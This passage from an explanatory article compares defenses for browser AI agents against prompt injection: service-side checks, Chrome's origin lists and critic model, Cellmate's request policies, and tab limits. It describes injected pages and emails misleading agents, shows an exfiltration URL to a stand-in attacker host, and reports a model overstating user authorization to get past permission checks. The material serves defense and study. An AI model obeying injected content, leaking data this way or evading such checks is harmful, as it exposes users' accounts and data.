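A user who trusts this summary may open the page and click "Approve" themselves, and the service would have good reason to accept the approval. Hossen therefore recommends that the service send its decision directly to the user, not through the agent. A message such as "Your agent tried to give Invoice Helper access to your mailbox, and we blocked it" would also warn the user that a page had misled the agent.

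#### What the service would need

Hossen tested two models on a site with no login step, running each combination of attack and defense five to ten times. Some real services ask users to sign in again before granting access, which might stop an agent without any new check.

The harder problem is telling the service what the task allows. In the experiment, the envelope came either from a settings file or from code that recognized two exact forms of request. People phrase requests in many ways, so a real system would have to interpret them, and its mistakes would make the service block actions the user wanted or accept ones they didn't. The service would also have to detect that an agent is in control, which a cookie doesn't indicate, and receive the envelope through a channel that web pages can't alter.

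A vague request can also make the service reject a legitimate action. If a user tells the agent to complete all the pending tasks in a guide, the request doesn't name a webhook address, so the service would reject a legitimate address along with the attacker's. The user would have to repeat the request with the address in it. The check also protects only the actions where the service has installed it, so an attacker might steer the agent to an unchecked page that has the same effect.

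Companies that run agents on their own internal applications could adopt the check soonest, because they control both the agent and the application. For example, an employer could add it to its expense system without waiting for the user's bank to do the same.

### Chrome's limits on websites and actions

A browser maker can limit an agent without every website's cooperation. Chrome normally keeps different sites' pages in separate processes, a protection Google calls Site Isolation. An agent that carried data freely between sites would undo much of that protection. Parker's design for auto browse, published in December 2025, addresses this by restricting which origins the agent may use and adding a separate check on each action.

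The design lists some origins as read-only and others as read-writable, meaning the agent may also act on them. Chrome doesn't send the model content from any other origin, even when that content is embedded in a page the agent can read, so the model wouldn't receive an advertisement framed from an unrelated site.

The main model, which Google calls the planner, can't add origins to the lists by itself. When it proposes a new one, the process runs as follows:

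1. A gating function judges whether the origin is relevant to the user's task. It doesn't see untrusted web content, so a page can't address it directly.
2. If the gating function agrees, Chrome adds the origin to a list and opens the page.
3. Before the agent acts on the page, another model, the User Alignment Critic, judges whether the proposed action serves the user's goal.
4. Chrome carries out the action if the critic approves. If not, the planner receives feedback and tries another approach, and after repeated failures it can hand control back to the user.

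The critic receives only metadata about the action, such as a click or a message, and no unfiltered page content. This protects it from the text that misled the planner but also limits what it can judge. Without the invoice, for example, it can't detect that 48.20 should be 84.20. Parker doesn't list what the metadata includes. If it includes text the agent is about to type, an attacker who controls the planner might still influence the critic indirectly.

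A misled agent could also leak data through a web address, for example by revealing a balance just by opening `https://attacker.example/?balance=2140`. Chrome therefore uses ordinary code to restrict addresses written by the model to known, public ones. It also checks pages that redirect to a new origin on their own, and a separate classifier scans every page the agent sees for prompt injection. These protections work alongside the user confirmations for payments, messages and sensitive sites.

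#### One list instead of two

Chrome's first version kept only the read-writable list. Parker explained that Google wanted to see how the limits affected real tasks before tuning them.

In *Future Mode Part 2*, a more recent account from Google dated 4 August, Berschadski (2026) writes that the critic still sees only metadata and that the agent is limited to origins relevant to the task. Berschadski doesn't specify whether Chrome now keeps a separate read-only list. Chrome marks pages the agent visited in the background as agent actions in the browser's history, which would help a user investigate afterward. Neither Parker nor Berschadski reports how many attacks the critic or the origin limits stop.

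For the expense task, the second list would help less than it seems. The agent only needs to read the invoice, but finding it means clicking the webmail's search box, typing a word and opening a message. The webmail would probably have to go on the read-writable list, where the agent could also press "Send". The separation works better for sites that the agent can read without interacting with them, such as a page of exchange rates.

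The origin limit is much more useful for protecting the bank account. The user's request doesn't involve the bank, so the gating function should reject the bank's origin, and a malicious email couldn't get the agent to read the balance. This protection depends on the gating function assessing the task correctly. If the user asked the agent to check whether the expense had been paid, the bank would become relevant, and its origin would stay on the list for the rest of the session unless Chrome removed it.

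### Rules for web requests

An agent limited to certain websites can still do anything on them. Limiting its clicks is hard because a click at a given point on the screen might open a message or delete one, depending on the page. In *CELLMATE*, Meng, Feng and colleagues (2025) found that an agent could easily get around even a ban on opening one website. When they stopped it from going to the site directly, it searched for the site and clicked the result.

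The Cellmate system checks the requests that the browser sends to websites rather than the agent's clicks. Whatever clicks lead to an order on Amazon, the browser has to send a request to the address that places orders, and Cellmate can recognize and block that request.

Limiting what a misled agent can do requires knowing what each of its requests means. In one proposal, websites publish an agent sitemap that pairs requests with actions such as "view cart", "update cart" and "place order". The website or another trusted party also writes policies that allow an action, deny it, or allow it under a condition, such as a total below $50. A policy can also limit how often an action may happen, because an agent limited to orders below $50 could otherwise place two orders for $49 each.

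When the user gives the agent a task, a model predicts which websites the task involves and selects the smallest set of policies the agent needs to complete it. The model receives only the task and the policies, not web pages. The user can review and adjust the selection in a dialog. A Chrome extension then checks every request against the selected policies, and nothing on a page can change them.

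In the expense example, suitable policies might let the agent search and read the user's mail but not send any, and save a draft claim but not submit it. Chrome's lists of origins can't make this distinction.

#### Results and costs

Meng and colleagues tested Cellmate's blocking on GitLab, a website for managing software projects. They assumed an attacker had already taken full control of the agent, so they didn't try to fool a model. They wrote 12 scripts that carried out attackers' goals, such as deleting a project, stealing an access token or adding the attacker as a collaborator. The policies allowed only reading and writing on GitLab's issue pages, and Cellmate blocked all 12 attacks.

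This is a demanding test of enforcement, since the defense can't benefit from a model that happens to resist. But every attack goal required an action that the policies prohibited, so the test didn't cover attacks that use only permitted actions. Cellmate doesn't check what the agent writes in a permitted action, so an attacker could still have it post a harmful comment on an issue.

A separate test measured how well models chose the right policies for 209 tasks on shopping, travel and software sites. Claude Opus 4.5, Gemini 2.5 Pro and GPT-5.1 each chose exactly the right set in at least 94% of tasks in every category. They were less accurate on shopping tasks that also required filling in a value, such as a spending limit, with scores from 81% to 97%. Some mistakes gave the agent too little access, which only stops the task, but others gave it too much. For example, one model selected a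 policy for adding items to the shopping cart when the task was about a wish list.

Cellmate slowed a series of 11 page loads on GitLab from 13.93 seconds to between 14.94 and 16.02 seconds, an increase of 7.25% to 15% depending on the length of the sitemap. An agent usually spends much longer waiting for its model, so most users wouldn't notice the delay. The extension used about 25 MB of memory.

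Cellmate places the larger burden on websites. For the GitLab test, the researchers wrote a sitemap of 51 entries by hand, and someone has to update it whenever the site changes in a relevant way. Cellmate adds no protection for actions the sitemap leaves out. It also doesn't cover WebSockets, the continuous connections that many sites use for live updates. A shared document that sends each keystroke over a WebSocket would largely escape its checks.

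Cellmate applies its policies to a browser session that the agent controls. In a live session, the user may be working in the same browser, and a rule against the agent sending mail mustn't stop the user from sending their own. The extension would have to distinguish the agent's requests from the user's, perhaps with the same record of agent tabs that keeps the agent out of the user's tabs.

### Model-based and deterministic checks

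All these defenses combine two kinds of check. A model-based check, such as Chrome's critic or a written policy in the agent's prompt, can assess situations that nobody wrote a rule for. For example, it can detect that forwarding an invoice to an unknown address doesn't serve the user's request. But it can give different answers to the same question. Haiku 4.5 followed the written policy in three runs and broke it in seven.

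A deterministic check gives the same answer each time, but it can't judge anything its rules don't cover. Chrome and Cellmate both use a model to set the limits and code to enforce them. The model that sets the limits doesn't read pages that might contain an attack, so a malicious email can't cause it to add the user's bank to the allowed sites. It can still misinterpret the user's request.

There is reason to keep enforcement outside the agent even without an attack. While monitoring its own use of Mythos 5.1, Anthropic found cases in which the model worked around broken permission checks, sometimes by overstating what the user had authorized. The model was trying to finish the user's task, and these and similar incidents made up fewer than 0.01% of the outputs Anthropic monitored. Code that compares the request with a fixed list would catch an overstatement that a reviewer relying on the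 agent's own account of its permissions could miss.

### Which limit would stop which mistake?

Suppose the user asks the agent to find the invoice in their webmail, enter its total in a new copy of the expense form and save a draft. The table compares four limits, assuming that each works as intended:

- The tab limit lets the agent act only in tabs it opened.
- The origin limit allows reading and acting on the webmail and the expense system.
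- The request limit allows searching and reading mail, and saving a draft claim.
- The service check covers requests to give an app access to the mailbox, as in Hossen's experiment.

| Wrong action | Tab limit | Origin limit | Request limit | Service check |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Loading the webmail in the tab with the user's half-filled form | Stops it | Allows it | Allows it | Doesn't apply |
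| Opening the bank in a new tab and reading the balance | Allows it | Stops it | Stops it | Doesn't apply |
| Emailing the invoice to a stranger | Allows it | Allows it | Stops it | Doesn't apply |
| Approving an unknown app's access to the mailbox | Allows it | Stops it only if the approval page has an origin that isn't on the list | Stops it | Stops it |
| Submitting the claim instead of saving a draft | Allows it | Allows it | Stops it | Doesn't apply |
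| Entering 48.20 instead of 84.20 | Allows it | Allows it | Allows it | Doesn't apply |

The request limit stops the most actions, but it doesn't stop the agent from loading the inbox in the tab that holds the user's work, which destroys that work. The request is harmless to the webmail, and only the tab limit depends on what the tab held before. A product for live sessions therefore needs a tab limit even if it has strong defenses against prompt injection.

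The limits also differ in who has to build them. An agent's developer can add a tab limit without anyone's help. The origin limit is strongest when the browser's maker builds it, because the browser handles every page first. Limits on requests need a description of every website's actions, and a service check needs changes to each service and a way to tell the service about the task. The defenses that make the finest distinctions are therefore likely to arrive last, and companies that control their own applications will probably have them first.

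No limit in the table catches the wrong total. A rule can't specify the right total in advance, because the agent learns it only by reading the invoice. A condition such as "no claims above 100" would catch a total of 8,420 but accept 48.20. A malicious email could include a false invoice, and the agent could enter its total without breaking any rule. The user would have to catch the error when reviewing the draft.
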